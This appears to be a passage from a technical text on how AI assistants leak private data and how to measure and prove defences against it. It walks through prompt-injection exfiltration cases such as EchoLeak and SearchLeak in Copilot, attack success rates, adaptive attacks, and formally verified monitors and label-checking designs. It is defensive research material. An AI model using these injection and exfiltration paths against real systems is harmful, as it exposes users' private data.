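In the test with 12 and 3 fetches, suppose the true rates are 6% and 1.5%, and the author knows that Alice has one of the two numbers. The author's best strategy is to guess 48213907 after a fetch and 71650284 otherwise. This guess is right 52.25% of the time, rather than 50%, so the leakage is only 0.06 bits. But leaks accumulate over repeated emails, and if the author can send a hundred of them and count the fetches, the guess will be right about 90% of the time.

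When nobody knows the true rates, the tester has to estimate them, traditionally by counting how often each output occurs with each secret. *F-BLEAU* (Cherubin, Chatzikokolakis and Palamidessi, 2019) points out that counting is useless for an output that hasn't occurred before, since it gives no reason to prefer one secret to another. This is a serious problem for text, because an assistant may never write the same reply twice. *F-BLEAU* proposes training a program to guess the secret from the output and using its error rate on new data as the estimate. A *nearest-neighbour* method, for example, guesses the secret that produced the most similar earlier output.

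The nearest-neighbour method can need far fewer runs than counting. In one simulated system with 100 secrets and 10,000 possible outputs, where similar outputs usually came from the same secret, counting needed 35,016 runs for an accurate estimate, while the nearest-neighbour method needed 333. In another system, built so that neighbouring outputs came from different secrets, counting needed 22,908 runs and the nearest-neighbour method needed 29,863.

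No method can be best for every system. Wolpert's 1996 *no-free-lunch theorem* shows that, averaged over all possible relations between secrets and outputs, every method does equally well on outputs absent from the training data, including random guessing. Cherubin and colleagues conclude that no estimator is guaranteed to be accurate after a finite number of runs, although several converge on the right answer as the number of runs grows without limit. They recommend trying several estimators and using whichever converges fastest.

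An estimate of this kind is much better at showing that a leak exists than at setting an upper limit on its size. If a program guesses the secret well on new runs, as McDonald and Bar Or's classifiers did with encrypted traffic, an attacker could use the same program, so at least that much leaks. If it guesses badly, another program might do better. F-BLEAU also gives no confidence intervals, and its inventors note that calculating them for continuous outputs, such as response times, requires stronger assumptions about the system.

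European electronic passports show both the value of such estimates and the risk of overinterpreting them. Some passports took a different amount of time to answer a replayed message if it came from one of their own earlier sessions, so someone with a recording could recognise the passport and track its owner. Researchers proposed padding the response times. Cherubin and colleagues tested their tool, F-BLEAU, on padded data from four sets of passports, where random guessing is right half the time. On the two sets where an older tool had found evidence of a leak, F-BLEAU guessed correctly 62% and 65% of the time. On the other two it was right 51% and 54% of the time, which they count as successful attacks that the older tool missed. But with only about 1,000 examples, random guessing could easily be right 51% of the time.

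## What a demonstrated leak proves, and what a failed attack does not

One leak that others can reproduce refutes the claim that a system never leaks. A failed attack by email is much weaker evidence for that claim, because the claim covers every email anyone could write and the attacker tried only one.

Suppose a developer claims that no email can make Alice's assistant reveal her account number to the email's author. If a tester's email makes the assistant send the number to the tester's server, the claim is false, however many other emails the assistant has handled safely. If the tester's email fails, the developer learns only that this email failed on this occasion. A different email might work, and because the model's responses are partly random, the same email might work on another attempt.

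A demonstrated leak refutes only claims about the configuration, policy and adversary in the test. The tester's leak doesn't refute a claim about a version of the assistant without a fetch tool, or about an eavesdropper who sees only encrypted traffic. If Alice had authorised the author to receive her number, the same web request wouldn't break the policy. A single leak also doesn't refute a claim that the assistant leaks in fewer than 1% of runs.

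### What a demonstration needs

Developers often dispute reports of leaks, sometimes with good reason. A tester can settle most disputes in advance by recording five things.

| What to record | Example | What can go wrong without it |
|---|---|---|
| The policy that the leak breaks | the email's author may learn nothing about the account number | the developer replies that the policy allowed the release |
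| A planted secret or a paired control | a new random number for each run, or the same task with a harmless email | the digits came from somewhere else, or the assistant sends them even without an attack |
| The results of repeating the test | the number reached the server in 7 of 50 runs | the leak was a fault in the test |
| Versions and settings | the model version, the developer's instructions, the tools, the monitor's policy and the contents of memory | a later test fails, and nobody knows whether the developer fixed the leak or the tester used a different setup |
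| The path by which the data left | the server's log matches a request from the fetch tool | nobody knows which boundary failed |

A leak doesn't have to occur in every run to be reproducible. If it occurs in 7 of 50 runs, someone who repeats the test should find it at roughly the same rate, and even one leak disproves the claim that the assistant never leaks.

The evidence also has to come from where the data arrived, because an assistant's own report can be wrong. It may say it has sent the account number when no tool ran, or deny a disclosure it made, as the agent in the Singapore and Korea refund task did.

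### EchoLeak

The best-documented leak from a widely used assistant closely resembles Alice's case. Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions by searching their emails, files and chats. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs, part of Aim Security, found that an outsider could extract private data from it by sending an employee one email. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study of the attack, describes an adversary who can email the organisation but can't query Copilot and has no other access. The victim doesn't have to click anything, only ask Copilot a question that makes it retrieve the email.

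*Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) gives the finders' account of the three main safeguards that failed. A classifier should have stopped the prompt injection before it reached the model, but the email read like ordinary instructions to a human employee. A filter should have removed links to outside sites from Copilot's reply, but it missed some link formats. The browser loaded images only from approved addresses, but one approved Microsoft service would contact an outside address on request. Copilot's reply could therefore include an image whose address contained private data, and displaying the reply sent the data out.

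The inventory for Alice's assistant marked replies as "assumed safe: the app loads nothing from outside". EchoLeak shows how data can leak when an assumption like this is false. Ravia places the underlying fault earlier, at the point where an outsider's text could direct the model to use private data in its context, and calls it an *LLM scope violation*.

The researchers' earlier failures show how little a failed attack proves. Copilot's filter removed the first kind of link they considered. The browser's rule then blocked images from an outside server. One approved service could get around the rule, but only if the victim accepted an invitation. A tester who stopped at any of these points could have reported that the safeguards worked. An attack that fails at one safeguard also leaves any later ones untested.

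Microsoft changed the software on its own servers in May 2025 and published the vulnerability in June. According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft found no evidence that anyone had exploited the flaw. Because Microsoft runs the service and has changed it, outsiders can no longer repeat the original test. The evidence now consists of the finders' account and Microsoft's confirmation, so testers of online services need to record dates and results while the flaw still exists.

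### A leak from the system is not a property of the model

EchoLeak showed that Copilot, as Microsoft had assembled it in early 2025, could leak private data to someone who could only send it email. We can't infer from this how often the underlying model, which Ravia identifies as GPT-4, follows malicious instructions, because his account gives no success rate and the rate in Copilot wouldn't necessarily apply elsewhere. In an app that loaded nothing from outside, the same model could have written the same reply without sending anything to the attacker.

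The software developer Simon Willison (2025) attributes such leaks to systems that combine access to private data, exposure to malicious text and a way to send data out. He also disputes how new the attack was, calling it an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products.

A developer can break this combination without changing the model. Reddy and Gujral describe changes to the software around Copilot, such as removing certain links and embedded images from incoming content. These changes can block the path that EchoLeak used, but they don't make the model less likely to follow instructions in the next malicious email.

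A second leak from Copilot, in 2026, used a similar path. Varonis, the security company that found it, describes the attack in *SearchLeak* (2026). A link to Microsoft's own website carried instructions for Copilot's search feature. If the victim clicked the link, Copilot searched the victim's mailbox and put what it found into an image address. A safeguard meant to turn the image into harmless text acted only after Copilot had finished its reply, when the browser had already requested the image. As in the first leak, an approved Microsoft service, this time Bing, passed the request to an outside server. Bing was already on the list of approved addresses that Ravia published in 2025.

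Microsoft rates the flaw critical in its own record, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (4 June 2026). It says that it has fully mitigated the flaw, that nobody is known to have exploited it, and that customers need to do nothing. The record describes the cause only as a form of command injection, so the details of the path come from Varonis's account.

EchoLeak requires no click, so it refutes even a security claim limited to users who never open an attacker's links. SearchLeak doesn't refute that claim because it works only if the victim clicks a link.

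An assistant can also break a policy when there is no attacker. TechRadar's *Microsoft admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot* reports that a coding error let Copilot Chat process emails labelled confidential in users' Sent and Drafts folders. Microsoft identified the problem in January 2026 and deployed a fix. Resistance to injected instructions would not have prevented the error, because the fault was in the code that chose which emails to give the model. The error violates a rule against Copilot opening confidential emails, but not a rule that only forbids sending them to outsiders.

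The success rate of prompt injection attacks on a model can vary widely with the system around it. Anthropic tested Claude Opus 4.5 as a browser agent against an automated attacker that made up to 100 attempts in each test environment. The attacks succeeded 8.0% of the time against the model alone, 7.6% with the company's older safeguards and 1.4% with improved ones.

The range is wider for a later model, Claude Opus 4.8. On a general benchmark, 0.5% of single attempts succeeded, according to figures quoted in *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (Schneier, 2026). In a browser, the figure was 31.5% without safeguards and 0.5% with them, according to VentureBeat's *Anthropic's browser agent got hijacked 31.5% of the time before safeguards engaged*.

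An attack's success rate also depends on how it reaches the model. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that GPT-5.6 Sol failed on about 0.05% of attacks sent directly through chat but 3.77% of those hidden in outside content.

These comparisons are rough because both the attacks and the systems differed between tests. The figures also count successful prompt injections, which need not involve a secret, so none of them measures how often Alice's assistant would leak her account number.

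### Open and closed channels

A leak test can return zero because the defence kept the secret out of the model's context, or because the model had the secret but didn't repeat it. Alpay and Alpay built AgentSecBench to record which happened.

Alpay and Alpay used three kinds of attack. In the first, a document ended with an instruction to print a marker. In the second, the context included a different customer's record with a canary in it, and a comment contained an instruction to reveal the canary. In the third, the result of one tool contained an instruction to use a forbidden tool. There were eight tasks of each kind, and each task had a harmless control that was identical except for the attack. They ran all of the tasks and controls on two very small models, Qwen3-0.6B and Qwen3-1.7B, with each of five defences and with none, for a total of 576 runs.

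No marker or forbidden action appeared in any of the 288 control runs, so the attacks caused the violations in the other runs. The controls also show when a defence prevents leaks only by making the model refuse everything, because the model then fails the harmless tasks too.

In the attacks on another customer's record, the canary appeared in 3 of 16 replies without a defence, and in 9 of 16 when the software put markers around the untrusted text and told the model to treat it as data. It appeared in none of the 16 replies when the software removed the other customer's record before the model received it. The increase from 3 to 9 is suggestive, but a difference at least that large would arise by chance about 7% of the time, even if the attempts were independent.

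All the defences combined stopped all 48 attacks. But Alpay and Alpay warn that a canary count of zero doesn't prove zero leakage, because the model could paraphrase a secret or disclose something correlated with it. The tests of forbidden tools count only what the model proposed to do, and no tool actually ran.

To separate the two reasons for a zero, Alpay and Alpay check whether the forbidden text is still in the model's input after the defence has acted. If it is, the channel is *open*, and if not, it is *closed*. Let *q* be the probability that the channel is open, and let *p*_open and *p*_closed be the probabilities of a violation in each case. The overall risk is

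$$R = q\,p_{\text{open}} + (1-q)\,p_{\text{closed}}.$$

The defence that removed other customers' records shows how this works. It closed the channel in the 16 attacks on such records but left it open in the other 32, so *q* is 2/3. None of the 16 closed attacks succeeded. Of the 32 open ones, 16 succeeded, all of them attempts to make the model choose a forbidden tool. The risk is therefore

$$R = \tfrac{2}{3}\times\tfrac{1}{2} + \tfrac{1}{3}\times 0 = \tfrac{1}{3}.$$

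This defence reduced the overall figure only slightly, from 37.5% to 33%, but it stopped every leak of another customer's canary, which the average alone does not show.

The formula works only if the rates are calculated over all runs. For a filter that removed suspicious lines, the paper gives *q* as 45.8% and *p*_open as 6.2%. Their product is 2.8%, but the measured risk was 4.2%. The 6.2% appears to be an average over types of attack. Two of the 22 open attacks succeeded, or 9.1%, and with that figure the formula gives 4.2%.

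Closing a channel limits the risk of a leak even when attacks improve. Suppose a defence keeps Alice's account number out of the context in 90% of tasks, and an attack succeeds 2% of the time when the number is there. The risk is 0.2%. A better attack that succeeds 90% of the time would raise the risk to 9%, but no attack could raise it above 10% if nothing leaks through the closed channel. If the number were always in the context, the same improvement would raise the risk from 2% to 90%.

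This limit holds only if the attacker can't influence *q*. The email can't affect a rule that withholds the number unless Alice's own request needs it. But if the system instead filters for suspicious phrases, an attacker can reopen the channel by rewording the email.

### Attackers who adapt

Most tests of defences use a fixed list of attacks, often written before the defence existed. A real attacker can study the defence and revise the attack after each failure. Security researchers call this an *adaptive* attack.

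*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr and colleagues, 2025) tested twelve published defences against adaptive attacks. For most of them, the original papers had reported that almost no attacks succeeded. According to the summary in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026), adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve, and human attackers reached 100%.

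The original tests may have been accurate, but they measured resistance only to the attacks on the list, and readers took this as resistance to attackers in general. Narisetty and colleagues give the example of Attention Tracker, a detector that scored perfectly on standard benchmarks. It missed 69% of the attacks in a different set, and all of them after a small change to the attack text.

These results don't show that every defence will fail. The twelve defences tried to make the model resist malicious text, or to detect that text before or after the model processed it. Defences that enforce rules outside the model pose a different problem for an attacker, but Narisetty and colleagues warn that researchers have tested these mostly against fixed attacks too.

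A failed attack is more informative if the attacker knew how the defence worked and had time to try alternatives. For example, if ten skilled people spend a month trying to break a defence and fail, that is much better evidence than the failure of a thousand old attacks run in an afternoon. A tester who reports failed attacks should therefore state what the attackers knew, how many attempts they made and whether they could change the attack between attempts.

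### Success over repeated attempts

An attacker who can send Alice one email can usually send a hundred, so the success rate of a single attempt can understate the risk. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports results from a benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan. Strong attacks on Opus 4.5 succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. Narisetty and colleagues give the same figures but attribute them to a Gray Swan test of coding agents.

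If every attempt had an independent 4.7% chance of success, the figures for ten and a hundred attempts would be

$$1-(1-0.047)^{10}\approx 38\%,\qquad 1-(1-0.047)^{100}\approx 99\%.$$

The measured rates are lower, especially for a hundred attempts. The most likely explanation is that some targets are much harder to attack than others. Suppose each attempt has a 7.5% chance of success against 63% of targets and no chance against the other 37%. The average success rate is still 4.7% for one attempt, but it is 34% for ten attempts and 63% for a hundred, almost exactly as measured. Further attempts add little because they are mostly made against targets that have already been broken or can't be broken.

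Differences between targets always shift the result in this direction. With more than one attempt, 1 − (1 − *p*)^*k* rises more and more slowly as *p* increases, so its average over unequal values of *p* is less than its value at the average *p*. Attempts that resemble one another have a similar effect, because if one fails, the others probably will too.

The three published figures can't show whether the hard cases are safe. If each attempt on a hard case had a 1 in 10,000 chance of success, the overall success rate would still be about 63% after a hundred attempts, but it would reach 86% after 10,000. A developer claiming that an assistant withstands thousands of attempts therefore needs to test it with thousands of attempts.

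Attacks succeed much less often against newer models. Schneier's July 2026 post gives a success rate against Claude Opus 5 of 0.2% after one attempt and 2.0% after fifteen. The rates for its predecessor, Opus 4.8, were 0.5% and 5.5%. If the attempts were independent, the rates after fifteen would be about 3.0% for Opus 5 and 7.2% for Opus 4.8, so the measured rates are again lower. GPT-5.6 Sol's rate after fifteen attempts was 20.0%.

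These results come from a newer benchmark than the one used for Opus 4.5. According to TechFeed, a Japanese news aggregator, Anthropic developed it with Gray Swan and the British and American government institutes for AI safety and standards. The new benchmark replaced one on which Claude models had near-perfect scores. The fall from 4.7% to 0.2% may therefore be partly due to the change of benchmark, but the scores showing an improvement from Opus 4.8 to Opus 5 are directly comparable.

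Readers also have to check what a percentage measures. A *per-attempt* rate is the share of attempts that succeed, and a *per-scenario* rate is the share of test environments in which at least one attempt succeeds. Suppose a tester makes ten attempts in each of 100 environments and 50 attempts succeed. The per-attempt rate is 5%, but the per-scenario rate could be anywhere from 5%, if all the successes occurred in five environments, to 50%, if each occurred in a different one.

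The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attack on Opus 5 as a browser agent succeeded in any of 129 test scenarios. This is a strong result for that product and those attacks. But even if the scenarios were a random sample of what an attacker might try, the result would be consistent with attacks succeeding in up to 2.3% of all such scenarios.

An earlier test in which no attack succeeded shows why such a result shouldn't be extended to other systems. VentureBeat reports that all 200 prompt injection attempts against Claude Opus 4.6 failed in a restricted coding environment. When the same model operated a graphical interface, with extended reasoning on and no safeguards, the attacker succeeded 17.8% of the time with one attempt and 78.6% of the time within 200. With safeguards, the success rate within 200 attempts was still 57.1%.

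## Enforcing the policy outside the model, and proving that it holds

Most of the defences that adaptive attackers defeated relied on the language model to ignore malicious text, or on a detector to recognise it. A developer who wants a proof can avoid relying on either by assuming that the model may output anything, including what an attacker wants, and letting trusted code decide which outputs take effect. For example, if Alice's assistant outputs a request for a web page whose address contains her account number, nothing is sent until the code around the model carries out the request.

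A proof about such a system has the form "for every model and every email, the policy holds". Because it doesn't depend on how a particular model behaves, it stays valid when the provider updates the model or an attacker finds a better wording. The proof does require facts about the trusted code, which is far smaller than the model and which people can read.

### How FIDES handles Alice's email

In FIDES, the agent that Costa and colleagues built, code around each tool labels whatever the tool returns, either as a whole or field by field. For example, it can label an email's text as untrusted and the time that the mail server recorded as trusted. The context's label is the join of the labels of everything in it, and each tool call that the model then requests gets the same label.

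Before running a tool call, FIDES compares these labels with the tool's policy. Under a *trusted-action* policy, a call with real consequences may go ahead only if the choice of tool and all the arguments are trusted. Under a *confidentiality* policy, data may go out through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is allowed to read the data. The confidentiality policy alone doesn't stop prompt injection. An email could still make the assistant fetch a page, but the policy would keep the account number out of the page's address.

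In an ordinary agent loop, these checks stop the attack on Alice. They also stop harmless requests, such as one for a weather forecast, because everything the model produces after reading the account number and the email counts as secret and untrusted.

FIDES avoids this by hiding data in *variables*. When a tool returns something that would raise the label of the context, the code stores it in a variable and shows the main model only the variable's name, such as `#email`. The main model can pass this name to another tool, and the code substitutes the contents just before the call. If a task requires reading the contents, the main model can send a question about them to an *isolated model*, which has no tools. The code stores the answer in a new variable, whose label is the join of the context's label and the labels of everything the isolated model read.

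| Step | Ordinary loop with labels | FIDES |
|---|---|---|
| Alice asks for a summary | the context is trusted and public | the context is trusted and public |
| The assistant looks up the account number | the context becomes secret | the number goes into `#account`, and the context stays public |
| The assistant reads the email | the context becomes untrusted as well | the text goes into `#email`, and the context stays trusted |
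| A model reads the injected instruction | the main model requests a fetch with the number in the address, and the check refuses it | the isolated model may obey, but it can only write text |
| Alice asks for a weather forecast | the check refuses the request | the check allows the request |

The summary in FIDES can't contain the account number, because the isolated model received only the email. If the main model had sent the isolated model both variables, the summary would be untrusted and secret, and the check would block it from being sent to a public web address. The email's author can still spoil the summary. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email containing an instruction to return an empty summary.

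Variables also allow more precise policies. If Alice asks the assistant to send the summary to her sister, the policy can require a trusted recipient while accepting untrusted text in the message. The recipient comes from Alice's request, so the email can't change it.

Some tasks depend on what the email says. Suppose Alice wants a calendar entry if the email requests a meeting. The isolated model answers yes or no, and software prevents it from writing anything else. The main model reads this answer. If it is yes, the main model has the isolated model extract the date and time into another variable, which goes straight to the calendar tool.

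FIDES records each answer's type in its label, so a policy can accept an untrusted yes or no in places where it would reject untrusted text. A single yes-or-no answer gives the email's author one bit of influence. But under the rule for joining types, a combination of yes-or-no answers still counts as yes-or-no, so the label is the same whether the author controlled one bit or 27.

### What explicit secrecy covers

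Costa and colleagues prove that their labelled loop can enforce *explicit secrecy*, which forbids a system to copy or compute secret data into public data. Take any sequence of steps that the system can carry out, and let *g* be the combined effect of those steps, so that *g*(*d*) is the stored data afterwards if it was *d* before. Write *d*₁ =ₗ *d*₂ if *d*₁ and *d*₂ contain the same public data. Explicit secrecy requires

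$$\text{for all } d_1,\ d_2:\quad d_1 =_L d_2\ \Rightarrow\ g(d_1) =_L g(d_2).$$

This is noninterference along one fixed path. If the path puts the account number into a web address, two different numbers produce two different public requests, so the path fails the requirement. But the definition does not cover whether the secret determined which path the system took.

Suppose a web search returns two addresses, which FIDES keeps in variables labelled untrusted and public. The assistant inspects the account number and fetches the first address if the last digit is even, or the second if it is odd. The confidentiality policy allows either fetch because both addresses are labelled public. Explicit secrecy also holds, because all account numbers that lead to the same path produce the same request. An observer still learns whether the number is even or odd, and 27 well-chosen decisions of this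 kind would reveal all eight digits.

The same gap appears in Tagged Branch, one of Dongol's test agents. Its plan queries a quarantined model and sends the attacker 1 or 0 depending on the answer. Both digits are public constants, so every message passes the label check, even though the quarantined model can base its answer on Alice's private notes.

Costa and colleagues accept this gap deliberately. They say that closing it would essentially require the system to forbid every call with public effects after any call that may read a secret. They also leave timing and packet length out of their model.

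Their proof treats the language model as a deterministic function. A model that chooses words at random fits this assumption only if we regard its random choices as fixed before the run.

### FIDES on AgentDojo

The AgentDojo benchmark has 97 user tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack environments, with attacks hidden in the data that tools return. Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on it in 2025 with GPT-4o, using attacks that name the agent's tools.

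| Design | Successful attacks without policy checks | With policy checks |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent loop | 152 | 0 |
| FIDES | 21 | 0 |

These counts leave out cases that the researchers thought AgentDojo had scored incorrectly, such as attacks it counted as successful even though the check had blocked the tool call. Hiding data in variables prevented most attacks by itself. The remaining 21 succeeded because, without the checks, the main model could open an untrusted variable and then continue as usual.

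The zeros depend on correct labels. The researchers marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, which a developer facing unknown attacks can't do. They also hid data based on whether it was untrusted, not whether it was secret. They did not restrict the isolated model's answers to fixed choices, so the test provides no evidence about policies that accept an untrusted yes-or-no answer.

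A policy can also permit actions that aren't sensible. In one banking task, the agent had to change the user's password if it found a suspicious transaction. It could see the amounts but not the descriptions, which were stored in variables. It treated a large payment as suspicious and changed the password without reading the description. The policy allowed the change because no untrusted data had influenced the decision.

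### LLMbda and implicit flows

LLMbda, a small programming language that Garby and colleagues designed for writing agents, also covers the implicit flows that explicit secrecy does not cover. Every value and every conversation with a model has a label. The interpreter tracks another label for the program context, so anything a program does because of a secret counts as secret.

This also applies to code the model writes. When a model's reply contains a program, the interpreter runs it under the label of the conversation that produced it. A model that has read a malicious email can therefore write any program, but the program's results will be untrusted.

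Developers can build an isolated model from two ordinary commands, `fork`, which makes a temporary copy of a conversation, and `clear`, which empties one. A program can fork the main conversation, clear the copy and have the model read an email there, so the email never enters the main conversation.

Only the `endorse` command can make untrusted data trusted, and reviewers can search for it in the code. In one example, a model sorts an email into a category, and the agent uses the category as the subject of its reply. The tool that sends email requires a trusted subject, so the program endorses the category after checking that it is on a short list. With eight categories, the email's author controls at most three bits of the subject.

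The central theorem is *termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference*. In plain words, data that an observer may not see can affect whether a run finishes, but it has no other effect on what the observer sees. To state this precisely, write *x* ∼ₘ *y* if two starting states differ only in data hidden from an observer at level *m*. Let *D*ₓ(*v*) be the probability that a run from *x* finishes with the observer seeing *v*. The theorem is

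$$x \sim_m y\ \Rightarrow\ \text{some } \omega \text{ satisfies } \sum_v \omega(v) \le 1 \text{ and, for all } v,\ D_x(v) \le \omega(v),\ D_y(v) \le \omega(v).$$

This is the compatibility condition discussed earlier for runs that a monitor stops. For programs without `endorse`, it holds at every level *m*, so it covers integrity as well as confidentiality. An observer who sees only trusted data can't tell which email the assistant read, except perhaps from whether the run finished.

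The proof constructs ω with an imaginary interpreter that skips each computation as soon as its label becomes hidden from the observer, and puts an empty placeholder in the result. This interpreter never uses the hidden data, so it gives the same distribution ω for *x* and *y*. Some of the skipped computations might have got stuck, so it produces each view at least as often as the real interpreter does. Therefore *D*ₓ ≤ ω and *D*ᵧ ≤ ω, as the theorem requires.

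Once a program uses `endorse`, the theorem still holds for confidentiality, but the integrity guarantee no longer covers the endorsed data. Garby and colleagues prove that neither endorsement nor the attacker's choice of untrusted input can cause secrets to leak, apart from what an observer learns from whether a run finishes.

### A proof about the program that runs

Many security proofs concern a mathematical model of a system, and the actual software may differ from it. Garby and colleagues reduced this gap by writing their interpreter in Lean, a language for both running programs and proving theorems about them. Lean checks every step of each proof. In the proof, the AI model's replies come from a table filled in at random before the run. They prove that running the interpreter with such a table gives exactly the distribution that the noninterference theorem describes.

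The theorem therefore rules out mistakes in label tracking, like CaMeL's failure to account for skipped branches. The researchers found another mistake in CaMeL, which treated the result as trusted when an untrusted value was inserted into fixed text.

The proof does not cover the code that contacts the model's provider over the network. It also assumes that each reply depends only on the conversation so far and on chance, which would be false if the provider also drew on a user's other conversations.

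The handling of tools is a larger gap. In the tests, the bank account and files were data inside the LLMbda program, and Garby and colleagues acknowledge that a better model would include outside tools. The theorem compares the results of finished runs, but a real email may go out before the interpreter stops a run, and the recipient can read it even though the run never finished.

### Why two attacks succeeded

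Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori in LLMbda and tested it on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. They paired each task with each of nine attacks and ran every pair three times with each of three models. There were 1,296 runs in total, and two attacks succeeded.

Both used GPT-5.2 and the same combination of task and attack. The user asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. A payment tool that requires trusted arguments would normally reject details from such a file. But the program the model wrote for this task endorsed the contents, so the agent paid the attacker.

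This doesn't contradict the theorem. The attack diverted money but revealed no secret, and an endorsement in the program had explicitly removed the integrity protection that would have prevented it. The model wrote that endorsement before reading the file, so the attacker didn't cause the endorsement. Without it, the interpreter blocks the payment, but also blocks an honest payment request in the same file, because both requests come from the same untrusted source and have the same label.

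The figure of 2 in 1,296 makes this weakness look rarer than it is. That combination ran only three times with GPT-5.2, and the attack succeeded twice. In about two thirds of the combinations, the attack needed a tool that the agent's program was unlikely to call, so a plan written in advance would usually have stopped it without labels. The 423 runs of the remaining combinations are a better test of the label checks.

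Even a plan written in advance can give an attacker control. In a test of CaMeL without its policy checks, a user asked the system to follow a file's instructions precisely. The model wrote a loop that read each instruction and called the matching tool. The plan never changed, but whoever wrote the file could choose what the agent did.

### Dongol's fence

A *fence* protects Alice more simply, without labels on individual values. The monitor removes any tool that an injected instruction could call by the time the assistant first reads untrusted content. Dongol notes that this amounts to FIDES's trusted-action policy with a single label for the whole context.

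His *fence theorem* shows that the assistant is then relatively secure, so an injection can't help the attacker tell apart any secrets that the plan wouldn't already let it distinguish. The theorem covers every plan and every email under these conditions:

- Each injected instruction makes a single tool call, and the fence covers every tool it can call.
- No trusted input gives those tools back.
- The model obeys injected instructions on a schedule that doesn't depend on secrets or on the monitor's responses.
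- The software meets the seven conditions listed earlier, such as sending every call through the monitor.

The theorem applies to an event-level attacker, who sees the content and order of messages but not their timing. For an assistant that runs indefinitely, it also requires that the model not keep obeying injected instructions forever.

The proof compares the assistant, step by step, with the reference agent, whose model never obeys injected instructions. Whenever the assistant makes an injected call, the monitor silently denies it while the reference agent waits. At every other step, both take the same action and get the same response from the monitor. The attacker therefore sees the same messages from both.

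The timing of the fence matters. In three of Dongol's examples, the plan itself specifies when the monitor removes the message-sending tool.

| Example | Order of steps | What an injection can send |
|---|---|---|
| Early Fence | remove the tool before reading the email | nothing |
| Middle Fence | read the email, remove the tool, read the secret | data already in memory, such as notes from an earlier session |
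| Late Fence | read the email, read the secret, remove the tool | the secret as well |

In Middle Fence, the model can obey the email immediately, while it still has the tool and its memory of earlier work. Removing the tool before the assistant reads the secret therefore does not guarantee Alice's protection, though a developer might expect it to.

The drawback of a fence is that the assistant can't use those tools after reading an email, so it can't reply to Bob's meeting request. A developer can partly avoid this by moving messages that don't depend on the email to the start of the plan. In Budget First, the agent may send only one message, and it sends Alice's calendar before reading anything untrusted, so an injection can't make it send another.

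An assistant that handles one email after another needs its tools back between emails. In the Stale Loop example, the monitor restores the sending tool for the next email while the previous email is still in the context, so the model can still follow instructions in the previous email. Dongol's solution is a *session fence*, which restores the tools only when a new session starts with an empty context.

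Dongol proves these results in Isabelle, another program that checks proofs. He wrote about 31,600 lines with the help of Anthropic's Claude Code. Because Isabelle checks the proofs, nobody has to trust the AI's reasoning, but people still have to check that the definitions express the right security property. Unlike the LLMbda proof, this one concerns a small model language, so a developer has to show separately that the actual software satisfies the model's assumptions.

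### Comparing the three guarantees

| | FIDES | LLMbda | Fence theorem |
|---|---|---|---|
| Property | explicit secrecy | termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference | relative security |
| Adversary | tampers with data from untrusted sources and sees public effects | chooses all untrusted input and sees the public results of finished runs | writes the untrusted content, chooses which text the model obeys and when, and sees messages but not their timing |
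| Model behaviour covered | any deterministic function | any distribution of replies, including replies that contain code | single injected calls on a schedule fixed in advance |
| Main assumptions | correct labels and tool policies | correct labels, checks in the tools, and replies that depend only on the conversation and chance | a trusted plan written before any untrusted read, and a monitor on every call |
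| Exclusions | implicit flows, timing and packet size | whether a run finishes, timing, outside tools and the integrity of endorsed data | leaks in the plan itself, timing, harmful actions that leak nothing, and tools whose replies depend on the request |

The guarantees in the table aren't in order of strength. Tagged Branch satisfies explicit secrecy but violates relative security. An assistant designed to send Alice's calendar to everyone can satisfy relative security, but it violates noninterference if the calendar is secret.

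### State kept between requests

In long-lived assistants, data can also lose its label between requests. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, describe a user who asks an agent on Monday to save the details of an invoice, and on Tuesday to pay it. The invoice contains an attacker's bank account number and a malicious instruction. Either could cause harm on Tuesday, even if nothing happened on Monday.

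The SPA agent stores each result in three parts: the value, its label and a short description of what it contains. When the agent handles an invoice, the planning model sees only the description, which it wrote before the agent opened the invoice. The invoice's text therefore can't change the plan. When the plan retrieves the bank account number, the number still carries its untrusted label, so a payment tool that requires trusted input will refuse it.

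SPA also checks the whole plan before running any of it. The plan consists of six simple kinds of step, including tool calls, conditions and loops, so a program can follow every label through it. The program checks both branches of each condition, which avoids the problem of the branch not taken. It uses only the labels, not the values, so a rejection reveals nothing about Alice's account number. SPA doesn't ask the model to repair a rejected plan, so there is no retry loop that could leak information or let the model keep trying until a plan passes.

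Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo and on a new version that splits each task into several requests. On the original benchmark, attacks succeeded in only 0.4% of runs without label checks, because SPA writes its plan before reading anything. The checks reduced this to zero. On the new version, the checks reduced the rate from 0.3% to 0.2%. The remaining 0.2% appears to be two runs that the benchmark counted as successful attacks even though SPA had rejected the plans.

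These results provide little evidence about attacks that take effect only during a later request. Even when the researchers let the planning model see the stored values directly, attacks succeeded in only 0.6% of runs. They attribute this low rate to the benchmark's attacks, which target tool results and seldom try to influence later plans.

### The cost in completed tasks

Label checks stop harmless tasks too. The table shows the share of tasks each system completed without an attack. The figures for the ordinary loop and FIDES are simple averages over AgentDojo's four environments.

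| System and test | Model | Without label checks | With label checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent loop, AgentDojo | GPT-4o | 84.3% | 41.9% |
| FIDES, AgentDojo | GPT-4o | 60.6% | 50.0% |
| CaMeL, AgentDojo banking | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| Randori, AgentDojo banking | GPT-5.2 | not tested | 75.0% |
| SPA, AgentDojo | GPT-5.4 nano | 53.0% | 29.0% |
| SPA, tasks split into several requests | GPT-5.4 nano | 62.5% | 35.3% |

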